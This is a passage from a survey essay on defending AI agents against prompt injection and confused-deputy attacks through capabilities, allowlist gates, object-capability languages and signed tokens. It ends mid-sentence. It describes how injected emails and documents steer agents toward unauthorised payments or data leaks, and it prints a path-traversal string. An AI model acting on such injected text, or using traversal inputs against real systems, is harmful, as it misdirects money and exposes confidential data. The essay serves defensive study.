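*SecureClaw* (Ma and Schmid, 2026) divides the work similarly for agents that use outside services. In its example, an agent has to email an invoice to a manager for approval. A gateway stores the invoice and gives the agent a reference number with a short summary, such as the supplier, the amount and the due date. In the preview step, the agent proposes sending that invoice to the manager. The gateway adds the identity of the user and the session, and a policy engine ties its approval to the complete request, including the recipient and the version of the invoice.

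At the commit step, a separate executor checks that the approval matches, is recent and hasn't been used. It fetches the invoice and sends the email only after these checks pass. If the agent changes the recipient after the preview, the executor rejects the action.

In SecureClaw, only the executor can reach the email service. The agent can only fill in a request, much like the payment agent that has `pay_invoice` and no shell. By contrast, a Windows agent that submits command text can cause an effect in countless ways, and Jing's gate has to recognise them all, with a sandbox to catch what it misses. SecureClaw's design requires someone to put every service behind the executor, and the agent could bypass the executor through a single forgotten connection.

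Ma and Schmid tested the executor against an agent that an attacker fully controlled. The executor rejected all 25 attempts to tamper with or reuse an approval and accepted all four legitimate requests. In a separate payment test, it blocked a changed amount, a changed recipient, a forged approval and a repeated payment. All four attacks succeeded when the executor's checks were turned off. This comparison is cleaner than most of Jing's because it removes only the preview-and-commit boundary, but it includes only four attacks and one legitimate payment.

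On AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated office tasks with planted prompt injections, attacks succeeded 31.5% of the time with no defence and 0.64% with SecureClaw. On Agent Security Bench, another set of attacks, the rate fell from 91.7% to zero in 2,000 trials. The main tests used GPT-4o mini, a model from 2024, but the Agent Security Bench result also held for four other models, including GPT-5.6 Luna.

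Checking actions doesn't protect information that an agent has already read. In a small test of leaks, Ma and Schmid kept the executor but let the agent see the raw data, and secrets appeared in messages between agents in 5 of 24 attacks. When they replaced the data with reference numbers, no secrets appeared in those messages. In a set of 496 attacks, information still leaked in 3.2%, nearly always through the agent's final answer.

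SecureClaw reduced the share of ordinary AgentDojo tasks completed from 70.1% to 60.8%. After a refusal, it can suggest a safe alternative, such as saving a draft. In a sample of 50 tasks from Agent Security Bench, these suggestions raised completion from 70% to 86% without letting any attack succeed. CaMeL, a system that tracks where each value came from, stopped every AgentDojo attack in an adapted comparison, but completed only 31.0% of tasks under attack, compared with 56.6% for SecureClaw.

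The four AgentDojo attacks that succeeded against SecureClaw all used actions the policy allowed, and the executor carried out exactly what the policy engine had approved. Three involved the wrong person or missing context, and one changed the wrong item in a workspace. A more detailed policy could stop these actions, but someone would have to anticipate which recipients and items belonged to each task.

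Harm can also build up over several permitted actions, as with the split payment. Jing left colluding agents out of the Windows experiment, and the Linux gate checks consecutive commands separately. Agents can cause such harm without intending to collude. Kovrr's *Multi-Agent AI Systems* (2026), a security vendor's blog post, points out that three agents with modest permissions can together complete an action that none of them had authority to take. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (2026) proposes showing the reviewer what the next action would complete, given the steps already taken. For the payment agent, the reviewer would see that a second $6,200 transfer brings the order to $12,400.

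## The confused deputy: from a 1970s compiler to agent frameworks

The attacks that got past SecureClaw misused permissions the agent properly held, which made it a confused deputy. The term comes from an accident with a compiler in the 1970s. Hardy described the accident in *The Confused Deputy* (1988) and argued that it showed why computers need capabilities.

### The compiler and the billing file

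The accident happened around 1977 at Tymshare, a company that sold time on its computers. Its compiler was in a directory called SYSX. Customers started it by typing `RUN (SYSX)FORT` and could name a file to receive optional debugging output.

Tymshare also wanted to know which features of the programming language people used, so the compiler wrote statistics to `(SYSX)STAT`. To allow this, staff gave the compiler a "home files license", which let it write to any file in its own directory. That directory also contained `(SYSX)BILL`, the billing records.

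One customer learned the name `(SYSX)BILL` and gave it to the compiler as the file for the debugging output. When the compiler tried to open that file for writing, the operating system allowed it because the compiler had a licence to write in SYSX. The debugging output overwrote Tymshare's billing records.

Hardy found a problem with every version of the obvious fix, which was to make the compiler check file names. If the compiler refused all names in other directories, customers couldn't send output there even when they had good reason to. Programmers couldn't have made it refuse names in SYSX, because they wrote the code before that directory name existed. Such a rule would also have been too broad, since some people might have legitimate access to files there. Refusing `(SYSX)BILL` alone would protect only that file, and someone would have to revise the compiler whenever another sensitive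 file appeared. Changing the operating system's rules for opening files also caused problems, because each new permission created holes in programs that had been secure and each new restriction broke legitimate ones. The last time Hardy wrote the rules down, they contained fourteen "and"s and "or"s.

The code that wrote the debugging output was correct until staff added the licence, even though nobody had changed the code. From then on the compiler had two sources of authority, the customer's and its own, and it had no way to specify to the operating system which one to use for a particular write.

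Tymshare tried adding a system call that let a program "switch hats" between its own permissions and the customer's. Under the customer's permissions, the compiler's request to open `(SYSX)BILL` would fail. However, some applications soon needed more than two sets of permissions, and the method didn't extend easily to permissions for things other than files.

With capabilities, whoever installs the compiler gives it a capability for the statistics file, and the customer gives it one for the debugging output file. The compiler uses the first to write statistics and the second to write debugging output. A customer who isn't allowed to write to the billing file has no capability to pass on, and can't make the compiler write there by typing the file's name. The original system let one party name the file while another supplied the permission. A capability combines the name and the permission,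 so whoever chooses the file must also have the right to write to it.

### "ACLs Don't" and the dispute over web browsers

Most systems still keep names and permissions apart. An access control list (ACL) records who may use a resource, and the system consults it when a request arrives. Tyler Close argued in *ACLs Don't* (2009) that a system using this method cannot make correct decisions when more than two principals interact, because information it needs is lost as messages pass between them. At Tymshare, the operating system could tell that the compiler was asking to open a file, but not that a customer had picked it.

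Close's main examples came from the web. In cross-site request forgery, a malicious page makes a visitor's browser send a request to another site, such as the visitor's bank. The browser automatically attaches the cookie that keeps the visitor logged in, so the bank treats the request as the visitor's own.

That year a working group of the World Wide Web Consortium, which sets web standards, was designing a way for a page from one site to request data from another. The receiving site could use the request's origin, the site the page came from, to decide whether to answer. Close (2009) objected on the group's mailing list that if the recipient judges requests by their origin, a site can't safely include an identifier from a third party in a request.

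Close (2010) described a legitimate program that uses an outside storage service to copy one file to another. The program reads from one web address and writes to a second, and the service supplies both addresses. A dishonest service could supply, as the first, the address of a private document that the program is allowed to read but the service is not. The program would then fetch the document and deliver it to the service.

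The browser makers had several answers. Van Kesteren (2009), of Opera, suggested putting outside code in a sandboxed frame, which has its own origin and can only exchange messages with the main page. A sandbox helps with untrusted code, but in the storage example the code is trustworthy and only the address is bad. Barth (2009) argued that making request forgery less frequent was progress, even if some cases remained. Stachowiak (2009), of Apple, doubted that a formal advantage for capabilities would matter much in practice. Sites already relied on cookies and origins everywhere, and nobody had a practical replacement for the cookie that keeps a user logged in.

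Close proposed using web-keys instead. A web-key is a web address containing a secret that nobody can guess, and anyone who has the address gets access. Mark Miller, a co-author of *Capability Myths Demolished*, supported Close. Miller (2009) knew of no paper that had answered the capability researchers' analysis of confused deputies.

Stachowiak had the better argument about the web, which could not abandon cookies without breaking existing sites. But Close's objection applies more strongly to agents, because much of their work involves copying identifiers from one party's text into a request to another.

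### An agent with a payout tool

In *Gemini discusses Confused Deputy* (2026), a mailing-list thread that Miller started, the capability researcher Alan Karp defines the term: "A confused deputy uses its permissions on a resource designated by someone else." Suppose an agent reads a supplier's email and has a payout tool that can send money from the company's bank account. The agent is a confused deputy if it pays an account because the email named that account.

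| | Tymshare's compiler | The payment agent |
|---|---|---|
| The deputy's own authority | A licence to write in SYSX | A credential for the company's bank account |
| The outsider | A customer | Whoever wrote the email |
| What the outsider supplies | The name `(SYSX)BILL` | An account number |
| The check that passes | The compiler may write in SYSX | The agent may make payments |
| What selects the permission | A line of code written in advance | The model, after reading the email |

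Hardy's remedy works on the first four rows. If the agent can pay only by presenting a capability for a particular supplier's registered account, an account number in an email can't determine where a payment goes. The `pay_invoice` tool had much the same effect by looking up the account in the supplier register.

The last row is harder. The compiler had separate pieces of code for statistics and debugging, and a programmer who knew the purpose of each could attach the right capability to it. A model has no such fixed places to attach capabilities. Suppose the agent holds capabilities for forty registered suppliers, and one supplier writes that a dispute is over and the company must pay the invoice today. The dispute is still going on, but the agent pays because of the email. The agent properly held the capability and paid a genuine supplier, but the supplier's email determined which capability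 it used and when.

Surapani and colleagues point out two other differences. An agent's authority can pass through several people, programs and services, and the attack arrives inside a document or email, whereas Hardy's customer made an explicit request. In their example, a user asks an agent to summarise the invoices in an inbox. One email contains a payment request, which the agent passes to a finance sub-agent without mentioning that the user's task was read-only. The payment service receives a valid credential and can't detect that the request came from an email.

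Checking the permissions of the person who gave the agent its task doesn't help here. *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security* (2026) defines a confused deputy as an agent that reaches a resource its user isn't allowed to reach. For example, an employee without access to the personnel database asks the agent for everyone's salary, and the agent looks it up using its own access. Running the agent with the employee's permissions would prevent this. But the finance manager who asked the payment agent to handle the inbox is allowed to make payments, so the same check would allow the agent to pay the disputed invoice.

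In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* (2025), David C, technical director for platforms research at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, argues that developers can repair an ordinary confused deputy but that language models are "inherently confusable", because they predict the next piece of text without any firm boundary between instructions and data. He recommends safeguards outside the model that limit what it can do. He also likes a proposal to reduce a model's privileges to those of whoever wrote the text it is processing. While reading a supplier's email, an agent could then do only what the supplier could do, such as submit an invoice. A separate process would have to make the payment.

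### What capabilities can and can't prevent

Hardy showed that capabilities would have prevented one confused deputy attack. Rajani, Garg and Rezk proved in *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks* (2016) that capabilities don't prevent all such attacks.

Their proof uses a small programming language. A program consists of pieces of code that run with different levels of authority, plus a gap where the attacker can insert any code that runs with the attacker's own authority. Every memory location has an owner, and code may write there only if its authority is at least as high as the owner's. Let *T* be the set of locations the attacker wants to change. Starting from a given state of memory, a program is free from confused-deputy attacks if, whatever code the attacker inserts, at least one of these conditions holds for every location *r* in *T* when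 the program finishes:

1. The attacker has no control over *r*. Any other code the attacker could have inserted would have left the same value there.
2. The attacker could have written that same value to *r* directly, using only the attacker's own authority.

If the first condition holds, the attacker didn't affect anything, and if the second holds, the attacker didn't need a deputy. The overwritten billing file meets neither condition, because its contents depended on what the customer submitted and the customer had no permission to write to it.

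A compiler that works as intended can also fail the definition, because a customer's bill may properly depend on the size of the program the customer submits. Rajani and colleagues therefore let programmers mark code as endorsed if it deliberately acts on outside input, and the definition excludes endorsed code.

In their capability system, code can never obtain a capability that its own authority doesn't cover. This stops Hardy's attack, because the customer can't obtain a capability for the billing file to pass on. Three other attacks still work, and in all of them the deputy already has the capability it will misuse:

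- The attacker supplies a value. The deputy copies something the attacker wrote into a protected location, as when an agent enters an emailed account number in the supplier register.
- The attacker influences a decision. The deputy writes one of two fixed values depending on a yes-or-no answer the attacker controls. The email about the settled dispute works like this.
- The attacker exploits a stored capability. A location open to the attacker already contains a capability for a protected one, and the deputy uses it to write the attacker's data. An agent might follow a link in a shared task list and paste a supplier's text into the ledger behind it.

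Capabilities alone do prevent every attack if neither the deputy's unendorsed code nor the starting memory contains a capability for writing to anything in *T*. But then that code can never change the things the attacker cares about, so the company's payment agent couldn't make payments. Rajani and colleagues say this condition makes the language useless for almost all practical purposes.

Ordinary permission checks are more effective when the system also labels every value according to the least trusted source it came from. Unendorsed code then can't write a low-trust value to a protected location. A simple version tracks values only as the program reads and copies them. A full version also tracks decisions, so if an outsider's answer determined which branch the program took, everything written in that branch is treated as influenced by the outsider.

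| Attack | Permission checks | Capabilities | Simple origin tracking | Full origin tracking |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Attacker names the target, as at Tymshare | Succeeds | Stopped | Stopped | Stopped |
| Attacker supplies a value | Succeeds | Succeeds | Stopped | Stopped |
| Attacker influences a decision | Succeeds | Succeeds | Succeeds | Stopped |
| Attacker exploits a stored capability | Succeeds | Succeeds | Stopped | Stopped |

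Full tracking is guaranteed to prevent these attacks, with no conditions on the program or its memory, but it runs more slowly and blocks some harmless programs. With a language model it would block a great deal, since any text in the prompt might have influenced any part of the output. Once the agent had read one email, the system would have to treat everything the model wrote as influenced by the supplier, and would refuse every protected write that nobody had endorsed. CaMeL avoids some of this by tracking individual values outside the model.

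Surapani and colleagues write that the confused deputy can't arise under a strict capability discipline. That is true under Karp's definition, which concerns a resource somebody else designated. Rajani and colleagues also count cases where the deputy picks the right resource but an outsider influences what the deputy does with it. Their broader definition is more useful to a company with a payment agent, because the company loses the money either way. But it covers only changes to data, so it doesn't apply to leaks like the one in Close's storage example.

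### Three agent frameworks

A payment agent has to act on outside input, so something has to decide which uses of that input are acceptable. Per-call authorisation does this by checking each call's arguments. In *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization*, Mellafe Zuvic (2026) examined whether three common agent frameworks include such a check. The "capability gates" of the title are limits on which tools an agent can call, not unforgeable tokens.

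LangChain and its companion LangGraph are general frameworks for building agents. When a model requests a tool, they look up the tool by name, usually check that the arguments have the right form, and run it. This check doesn't catch an attacker's account number, because it has the same form as a legitimate one. Developers can add a step where a person approves the call, but it isn't on by default.

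LlamaIndex, another general framework, checks that the named tool exists, then passes it the model's arguments. Its description of each tool's arguments specifies their form but not which values are allowed.

The Stripe Agent Toolkit connects agents to the payment company Stripe. It has a list of permitted actions and uses a Stripe key whose permissions can also be restricted. Within those limits, it forwards whatever amount, currency and customer the model supplies.

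So all three packages restrict the choice of tools, but none authorises argument values by default. Mellafe Zuvic read only public code and didn't examine Stripe's remote servers, which may do more. The audit treats the gap as a documented design choice that leaves argument checks to developers, and it reports no formal vulnerability in any of the packages. A general framework can't come with rules for which accounts a particular company should pay, but it could block a payment tool until the developer supplies them.

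To demonstrate the gap, Mellafe Zuvic built a LangChain agent with a tool that changes a merchant's payout account in a simulated payment system. A fixed output, standing in for a deceived model, requested that the payout account be changed to `acct_ATTACKER_999`, and LangChain made the change. The test shows what the framework does with a bad call, but not how often a model would produce one.

A separate benchmark of 27 models, also by Mellafe Zuvic, measured how often models attempted a forbidden action when injected text presented it as a necessary part of the user's task. Twelve cheaper models attempted it in 60.3% of trials on average, and fifteen leading models in 18.9%. Rates for individual models ranged from 0% for a preview version of Gemini 3.1 Pro to 100% for GPT-4o mini. The wording of the injection also mattered a great deal. Mistral Large attempted the action in 2.7% of trials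 when the injection was crude and 45.9% when it matched the task. The benchmark blocked all real effects, so these are rates of attempted harm.

### ScopeGate's five checks

Mellafe Zuvic's remedy is ScopeGate, a program that sits between the model and its tools. A person writes its policy in advance, and no model takes part in its decisions. For each call it applies five checks:

1. Scope: the policy must list the tool.
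2. Authorisation: each restricted argument must have a value on that argument's allowlist. If the only approved payout account is `acct_MERCHANT_001`, a call naming any other account fails.
3. Money: the amount must be an ordinary number between zero and a ceiling.
4. Repetition: where the policy requires it, the call must come with a trusted key that identifies the operation, so that the payment service can recognise a retry.
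5. Default denial: ScopeGate refuses any call that doesn't pass all the other checks, including one that causes an error in ScopeGate itself.

ScopeGate blocked the change to `acct_ATTACKER_999` that LangChain had carried out. ScopeGate lists permitted values, unlike most of the similar file-name checks that Hardy rejected, which listed forbidden names and so exposed any sensitive file missing from the list. An omission from ScopeGate's list blocks a legitimate payment, an error that somebody will notice and can correct.

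In the fixed tests, ScopeGate blocked all 48 unauthorised calls. Many were disguises, such as an account name containing an invisible character or a lookalike letter from another alphabet. Others used misspelled tool names, strange amounts or missing keys. An exact allowlist ought to reject the disguises, so these tests are mainly useful for finding programming errors, and they found one. An earlier version refused amounts greater than the ceiling but let through NaN ("not a number"), a special value for which every such comparison is false. The corrected version requires the amount to lie within the allowed range.

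In the adaptive test, an attacking model, GLM-5.2, made 40 attempts and received ScopeGate's reason after each refusal. Nine attempts were malformed, two were harmless, and ScopeGate blocked the other 29. Even if those 29 had been independent random attempts, the true success rate could still be almost 10%. They weren't independent, because one model made them all, and a more skilled attacker might try something different. ScopeGate also allowed all ten legitimate calls in a test of false alarms, but by the same reasoning the true false alarm rate could be as high as about 26%. For a company with hundreds of payments a week, uncertainty about false alarms could matter as much as uncertainty about attacks.

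The published decision procedure also has gaps that these tests couldn't reveal. It applies the ceiling to each call separately, so with a limit of $10,000 it would allow both $6,200 payments for the chairs. It checks each argument against its own list, so it can't require that the account belong to the supplier on the invoice. Except for the amount, it doesn't check arguments that the policy leaves unrestricted. It uses session information only to find the repetition key, so it would need a separate policy for each user to account for who requested the payment. Although it can block the attacker's account number, the agent could still pay a disputed invoice to an approved supplier.

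The gate also has to be on the only route to the payment service. Surapani and colleagues describe a trade-off between checks near the model, which have more information about the task but are easier to bypass, and checks near the resource, which are harder to bypass but may identify only whose credential is in use. Mellafe Zuvic says ScopeGate can run inside the agent's application, beside it or at a central gateway, but tested it only inside the application. An agent with a shell and a payment key could bypass it there.

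### Who writes the allowlist

Mellafe Zuvic insists that no part of the policy may come from a model's output, even indirectly and even when staff prepare the policy long beforehand. The policy must also stay fixed for the whole conversation. Otherwise, text that corrupts a call could also corrupt the policy meant to stop it.

This is reasonable for paying known suppliers, since the company already keeps a register of them. But suppose the manager asks the agent to find someone to repair the broken chairs and pay a deposit of up to $200. Nobody can list the repairer's account in advance, because the agent hasn't chosen the repairer yet. The agent would have to choose a firm and stop, an employee would have to verify and add the account, and the agent would then have to make the payment in a new conversation. That is tolerable for a deposit but would be unworkable for an agent that has to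 visit a hundred unfamiliar websites to compare repairers, and its operator would probably end up allowing every address.

Ordinary users are unlikely to write the missing rules themselves, since those in Yan's study mostly chose to be asked each time. Several research systems therefore have a model draft the policy and conventional software enforce it.

*Only What You've Signed up For* (2026) has a model choose a policy based on the user's original instruction, and the policy stays fixed whatever the agent reads later. The model picks from existing constraints, and software fills in the sensitive values. This answers much of Mellafe Zuvic's worry about corruption, because an email can't influence a choice the model made before the agent opened it. The protection disappears if the user pastes the email into the instruction. The model can also misunderstand the request. To measure enforcement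 without that source of error, the researchers wrote a policy for each task by hand, which a company with open-ended tasks can't do.

In *Environment Steering* (2026), a model writes rules for each task. Given the request "Summarize patient Jane Smith's recent visit", it produced one rule that checks the answer against a blacklist and another that forbids mentioning other patients. According to the paper, such rules may be too strict, too loose or missing. The researchers corrected the rules for the first ten tasks by hand and used some of them as examples for the rest.

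*ActGov* (2026) asks a model for rules that apply to many tasks and can refer to where an argument came from as well as its value. Such a rule could require a payout account to come from the supplier register. A person could review the rule once, and it would cover suppliers who joined later. It would also make write access to the register as sensitive as access to the payment tool.

Hardy's solution suggests a different way to involve the user. His customer would choose and authorise the output file in one act, by handing over a capability for it. Likewise, the agent could present three repair firms, and the manager could select one on a screen that the harness controls. The harness would take the firm's account details from a source the agent can't edit and permit one payment of up to $200 to that account. The manager would only have to decide which firm to hire and wouldn't have to write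 a rule.

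## Object-capability languages and code written by agents

A user can hand over authority for one payment through a screen built for that purpose, but an agent that writes its own code may need a different combination of files and services every hour. Object-capability languages apply Hardy's remedy to every line of that code. A program can use an object, such as an open file, only if it holds a reference to it, which is the value through which code reaches the object.

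Most languages rely on ambient authority, so any line of Python or Java can open a file by giving its name as text. An object-capability language prevents this because code can't turn a string or a number into a reference, an object can keep its references private, and no global object gives access to files or the network.

A program can then obtain a reference in only three ways, which Habitat Chronicles' *What Are Capabilities?* (2017), an introductory blog post, sets out:

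- Creation: code that makes a new object gets a reference to it.
- Endowment: whoever creates an object can build references into it. The first file or network connection enters this way, because something outside the language has to supply it.
- Transfer: code that holds a reference can pass it on, but only to an object it can already reach.

Object-capability languages help a company that can't read everything its agents write. A reviewer can find the most that a script could do by looking at the references the harness gives it and what those lead to, without reading the script.

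### From MIT to JavaScript

Capabilities began in operating systems. In 1966 Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn of MIT proposed giving each computation a list of the things it may use. *Capability-Based Computer Systems* (Levy, 1984) explains that a program refers to a file by its position in the list, so it can't refer to a file that isn't on it. A program can also attenuate a capability, which means making a version with fewer rights, such as reading without writing, and pass on that version. IBM's System/38 of 1978 was the first major commercial computer to use capabilities.

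Programming languages later gave the same control over things much smaller than files. The language E came from Electric Communities, a company building an online world to which users could add their own objects. Its designers had to make sure that an axe programmed for a fantasy game couldn't kill anyone in a neighbouring stock exchange. Few people wanted to buy such a world, and the company moved into other businesses but kept the programming methods. Its developers recalled that more of their code then worked the first time. Nobody measured this, but it makes sense that rules against deliberate misbehaviour would also catch accidents.

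Joe-E is a subset of Java that Adrian Mettler, David Wagner and Tyler Close published in 2010. Java already stops code from forging references, but much of the benefit is lost because any code can open a file by naming a class, as in `new FileInputStream("passwords.txt")`. Joe-E removes such features from the standard libraries, so code can read a file only if other code passes it an open `InputStream`.

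JavaScript also let any script on a web page alter the built-in functions that other scripts relied on. Frozen Realms, a proposal moving slowly through standardisation in 2017, would run code in a locked environment, and the code could reach outside it only through references passed in from outside. Hardened JavaScript grew out of this work. Its `harden` function freezes an object and everything reachable through it.

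### Lending a folder and taking it back

Suppose an agent has to summarise this month's invoices. The harness holds `invoices`, an object that can list, read, write and delete files in one folder. In Hardened JavaScript, it could lend the agent's script read access like this:

```js
function lend(folder) {
  let target = folder;
  const reader = harden({
    list: () => target.list(),
    read: (name) => target.read(name),   // returns text
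  });
  const revoke = () => { target = null; };
  return { reader, revoke };
}

const { reader, revoke } = lend(invoices);
runAgentScript(reader);

// when the manager cancels the task:
revoke();
```

The script's access is attenuated because it receives `reader`, which has no method for writing or deleting, and can't reach `target`, which is private to `lend`. The harness keeps `revoke` and can call it to make every later request through `reader` fail, although `reader` still exists. If the script had passed `reader` to a sub-agent, the sub-agent would lose access at the same moment.

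Revocation can't take back text the script has already read. If `read` returned a file object instead of text, that object would keep working after revocation unless `lend` wrapped it too. Because `name` is an ordinary string, the script can also pass `../payroll/salaries.csv`, which the folder object has to reject.

### Three objections to capabilities

In 2003, Miller and colleagues answered three long-standing criticisms of capabilities: that they are just access lists in another form, that nobody can revoke them, and that they can't confine a program.

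The claim that capabilities and access lists are equivalent comes from a table with a row for each user and a column for each file. An access list is a column and a capability list is a row, so they seem to hold the same information. But the table shows permissions at a single moment, so it leaves out how they change. It also leaves out how a program indicates which file it means, which was the root of the trouble with Hardy's compiler.

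Access lists also have to name their users, and nobody can keep a list up to date with programs that start and stop all day, so in practice the lists name accounts. Two sub-agents running under one account therefore have the same permissions, while a capability system can give each its own references.

The objection about revocation is partly right, because once a program holds a reference, nobody else can take it away. But the owner can hand out a forwarder instead, as `lend` does, and later switch it off. David Redell described this method in 1974.

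The argument about confinement goes back to a 1984 paper by W. E. Boebert. For example, suppose a company has one script that can read the payroll, and another that can publish to the website and write to a folder that the payroll script can read. The publishing script saves its publishing capability in the folder. The payroll script then uses it to publish everyone's salary.

Miller and colleagues reply that this works only if a capability can be passed as ordinary data. Nearly all capability systems separate reading text from receiving a reference, so the company can provide a folder that carries only text. The payroll script then cannot obtain the publishing capability, because no chain of references could deliver it.

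The reply doesn't help if one script needs access to both the payroll and the website. References limit what a script can reach, but they don't stop it from copying data between the things it can reach.

### Names in the model's output

An object-capability language can limit a script to `reader` even if a hijacked model wrote it. But the model itself handles only text, and text can name anything. When an agent makes a tool call containing a file path, the harness has to turn that path into a reference. If the harness looks up the path using its own full access, it becomes a confused deputy like the compiler.

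The harness can avoid this by looking up the name only among the references it set aside for the task. The model still chooses among those references, and Rajani and colleagues proved that capabilities don't stop an attacker from influencing such a choice.

A tool's design can also reintroduce the naming problem. One recent system gives an airline's agent a `cancelReservation` function that takes a reservation number as text. The compiler can check that the argument is text, but not that the reservation belongs to the customer in the conversation. The harness could instead look up that customer's reservations and give the agent an object for each, with a `cancel` method. The agent could still cancel the wrong reservation, but only one of that customer's.

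### Scala programs that show which capabilities they use

Odersky, Zhao and colleagues built TACIT, described in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026), to deal with scripts that can access both a secret and a channel for leaking it. The agent writes programs in Scala 3 and submits them through an MCP server, and the Scala compiler checks each program before any of it runs.

In most typed languages, the compiler uses types to track what kind of value something is, such as text or a number. With capture checking, an experimental Scala feature, types also list the capabilities that the value can use. A function that writes text to a file `f` has the type `String ->{f} Unit`, where `{f}` records its access to the file. A function with nothing in that position is pure, so it can't write, send or change anything outside itself. E and Joe-E don't guarantee this, because they control references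 only while a program runs.

TACIT uses pure functions to protect secrets. When the agent's program reads a protected file, it receives the text inside a container called `Classified`, and it can process the contents only with a pure function:

```scala
secret.map(text => text.length)           // accepted
secret.map(text => outbox.write(text))    // rejected by the compiler
```

The result stays in a container too. If the program prints it, the user's screen shows the real contents but the agent gets only `Classified(****)`. To summarise a secret contract, the program can send the container to a separate trusted model and get the summary back in another sealed container. The main model never reads the contract, so instructions hidden in the contract can't reach that model.

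A sandbox couldn't provide this protection, because the agent needs permission both to read the contract and to contact its model provider, and the leak consists of moving text from one to the other. However, a TACIT program can start outside commands from an allowlist, and the compiler can't check what those commands do, so Odersky and colleagues recommend adding a sandbox. A program could also leak a little information through how long it takes to run.

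An agent's access to files depends heavily on who names them. In TACIT's general library, the agent's program asks for access to a folder by giving its path as text. The library blocks anything outside that folder and withdraws access when the block of code ends, but somebody still has to decide which folders the agent may ask for. In the paper's example of comparing contracts, a person has already chosen the document database and the output file, and the agent's program receives only those two objects.

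### How well agents work in Scala

To test for leaks, Odersky and colleagues gave agents a software project with a folder of secret keys and documents. They paired 12 ordinary tasks with 10 prompt injections each, and added 11 requests in which the user tried to extract the secrets directly, sometimes by posing as an administrator. Without the `Classified` container, Claude Sonnet 4.6 leaked secrets in 2 of the 131 trials and MiniMax M2.5 in 11, but neither model leaked any with it.

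The perfect score mostly confirms that the software works as designed, because the agent can't repeat a secret it never sees. Sonnet also resisted all 120 injections without the container, so the container couldn't improve its score in those trials. Less predictably, Sonnet completed 99.2% of the ordinary tasks with the container and 83.3% without it. Some of the difference may come from the setup, since Sonnet often ran out of time or stopped to warn the user about an injection.

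On AgentDojo, one of 1,926 injection trials with two other models using TACIT counted as a success for the attacker. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted a review that recommended the attacker's hotel. Task completion varied widely. With OpenAI's o4-mini, TACIT completed 52.9% of the office tasks, compared with 81.4% for CaMeL. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT completed 64.3% of the travel tasks, compared with 1.4% for CaMeL.

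Writing Scala didn't make agents noticeably worse at their tasks. On τ²-bench, a test of simulated customer service, three models scored between 0.8 and 3.7 percentage points higher when they wrote Scala programs than when they made ordinary tool calls. On 300 real software problems, MiniMax solved 41.7% with Scala and 43.3% without, a difference of about five problems. The compiler rejected some programs for ordinary coding errors, but in the τ²-bench runs fewer than 8% needed a second attempt.

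In *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026), the model's code becomes part of the program that runs the agent. The program contains a gap with a description of the task and the type of result it needs. When the program reaches the gap, the model writes code to fill it. The code can use whatever variables and tools are in scope at that point, so the position of the gap determines the agent's permissions.

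The compiler accepts or rejects each piece of code as a whole. In one example, a model has to subtract 50 from a balance of 100 and return the new number. Its code subtracts the 50 but then returns a sentence instead of a number. The compiler rejects the code before it runs, so the balance stays at 100. This protects against partial effects only when the compiler can find the error. Code that passes the check and then loses its network connection could still leave a job half done.

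LACUNA creates sub-agents by allowing the code in a gap to contain further gaps. By default, a sub-agent can use everything its parent could, plus any values the parent has computed since. That is convenient for solving problems, but it is the opposite of attenuation. A developer who wants a weaker sub-agent has to arrange the code so that fewer things are in scope. On τ²-bench, LACUNA solved 76.0% of 392 tasks, about the same as an ordinary agent.

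### Tokens that travel between services

A reference works inside one program, or between programs that share a way of passing references. Companies usually pass authority to each other as a token, a piece of text with a cryptographic signature. Macaroons, a 2014 design by Birgisson and colleagues, let the holder of a token add restrictions to it before passing it on.

In *Crypto-bound identity-verified capability tokens for coordinating distributed AI agents*, Subramanian and Sengupta (2026) propose signed tokens for chains of agents. In their example, a user gives a travel agent called Atlas a token with a $5,000 budget, and Atlas gives a flight-booking agent a token for $1,500 of that. The airline can follow the signatures back to the user and check that no step increased the authority.

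That check doesn't limit the combined total. Atlas could give four agents tokens for $1,500 each. Every token would be for less than the one it came from, but together they would allow $6,000, much as two payments of $6,200 can each pass a $10,000 limit. An airline checking one token can't see the other three. A forwarder can easily keep a running total because all the payments go through it, but with tokens, the services need a shared record.

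A simple token works for anyone who has its text, so an agent could expose one by pasting it into an email or a log. A reference can't leak this way because it has no text to paste, and a program can give it only to something it can already reach. Miller and colleagues accept that the objections about revocation and confinement are true of capabilities that work like copyable keys, so their answers to those objections don't cover a company that gives its agents simple tokens.

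One remedy is to tie the token to its holder, who must then prove an identity to use it. Subramanian and Sengupta would also keep the secret keys in a separate program, a wallet, so that they never enter the model's prompt. A thief then gains little from a copy of the token. But an attacker can still deceive an agent into using its own token on the attacker's behalf, and the wallet will sign whatever its rules allow.

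Subramanian and Sengupta consider it extremely difficult or impossible to revoke a token if the service checks it using only the information it contains. They would have the service ask a central checker whether each token is still valid, even though this adds delay. Short expiry times also help, since a stolen token that lasts 30 seconds is of little use to an attacker.

Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao (2026) built and tested a system along these lines in *AGENTCAP*. Each time the agent wants to use a tool, a policy engine decides whether to issue a signed token for that action. In their banking example, a payment token lasts 30 seconds and allows one call. The engine does not issue it if the recipient's name appears only in untrusted text, such as an email the agent has read. A gateway in front of the tool then checks the token and which agent is presenting it. An agent can delegate its token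 to another agent in the same session, but can't extend its lifetime or increase the number of calls.

On AgentDojo, the attack success rate fell from 45.6% to 5.1% with GPT-4o and from 33.2% to zero with GPT-5.4. Without attacks, the task completion rate fell by 3.1 and 7.2 percentage points, respectively. The benchmark tested all the checks together, so it doesn't show how much the tokens contributed. The check on where the recipient came from may account for much of the gain, and a system without tokens could make the same check. Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao also wrote the policies after reading the benchmark's task descriptions, an advantage that a company with open-ended work wouldn't have.

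### DelegateGuard

An organisation can avoid copyable tokens internally by keeping every grant in a central table. *DelegateGuard* (Tran-Truong, Vo and colleagues, 2026) describes such a design, in which an agent holds only an identifier for an entry in the table. Whenever the agent tries to move data, a monitor outside the model looks up the entry and checks that this agent is its holder.

In the paper's example, a user asks for a summary of a confidential contract, and the main agent delegates the formatting to a worker. A clause in the contract instructs the reader to send the contract's restrictive terms to an outside web address. The worker's grant only allows it to transform the text and send the result to the user, so the monitor blocks the outside address.

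Each grant lists a purpose, the labels of the data it covers, the permitted operations, the permitted destinations and the number of further delegations allowed. A child grant *c* made from a parent grant *p* must satisfy

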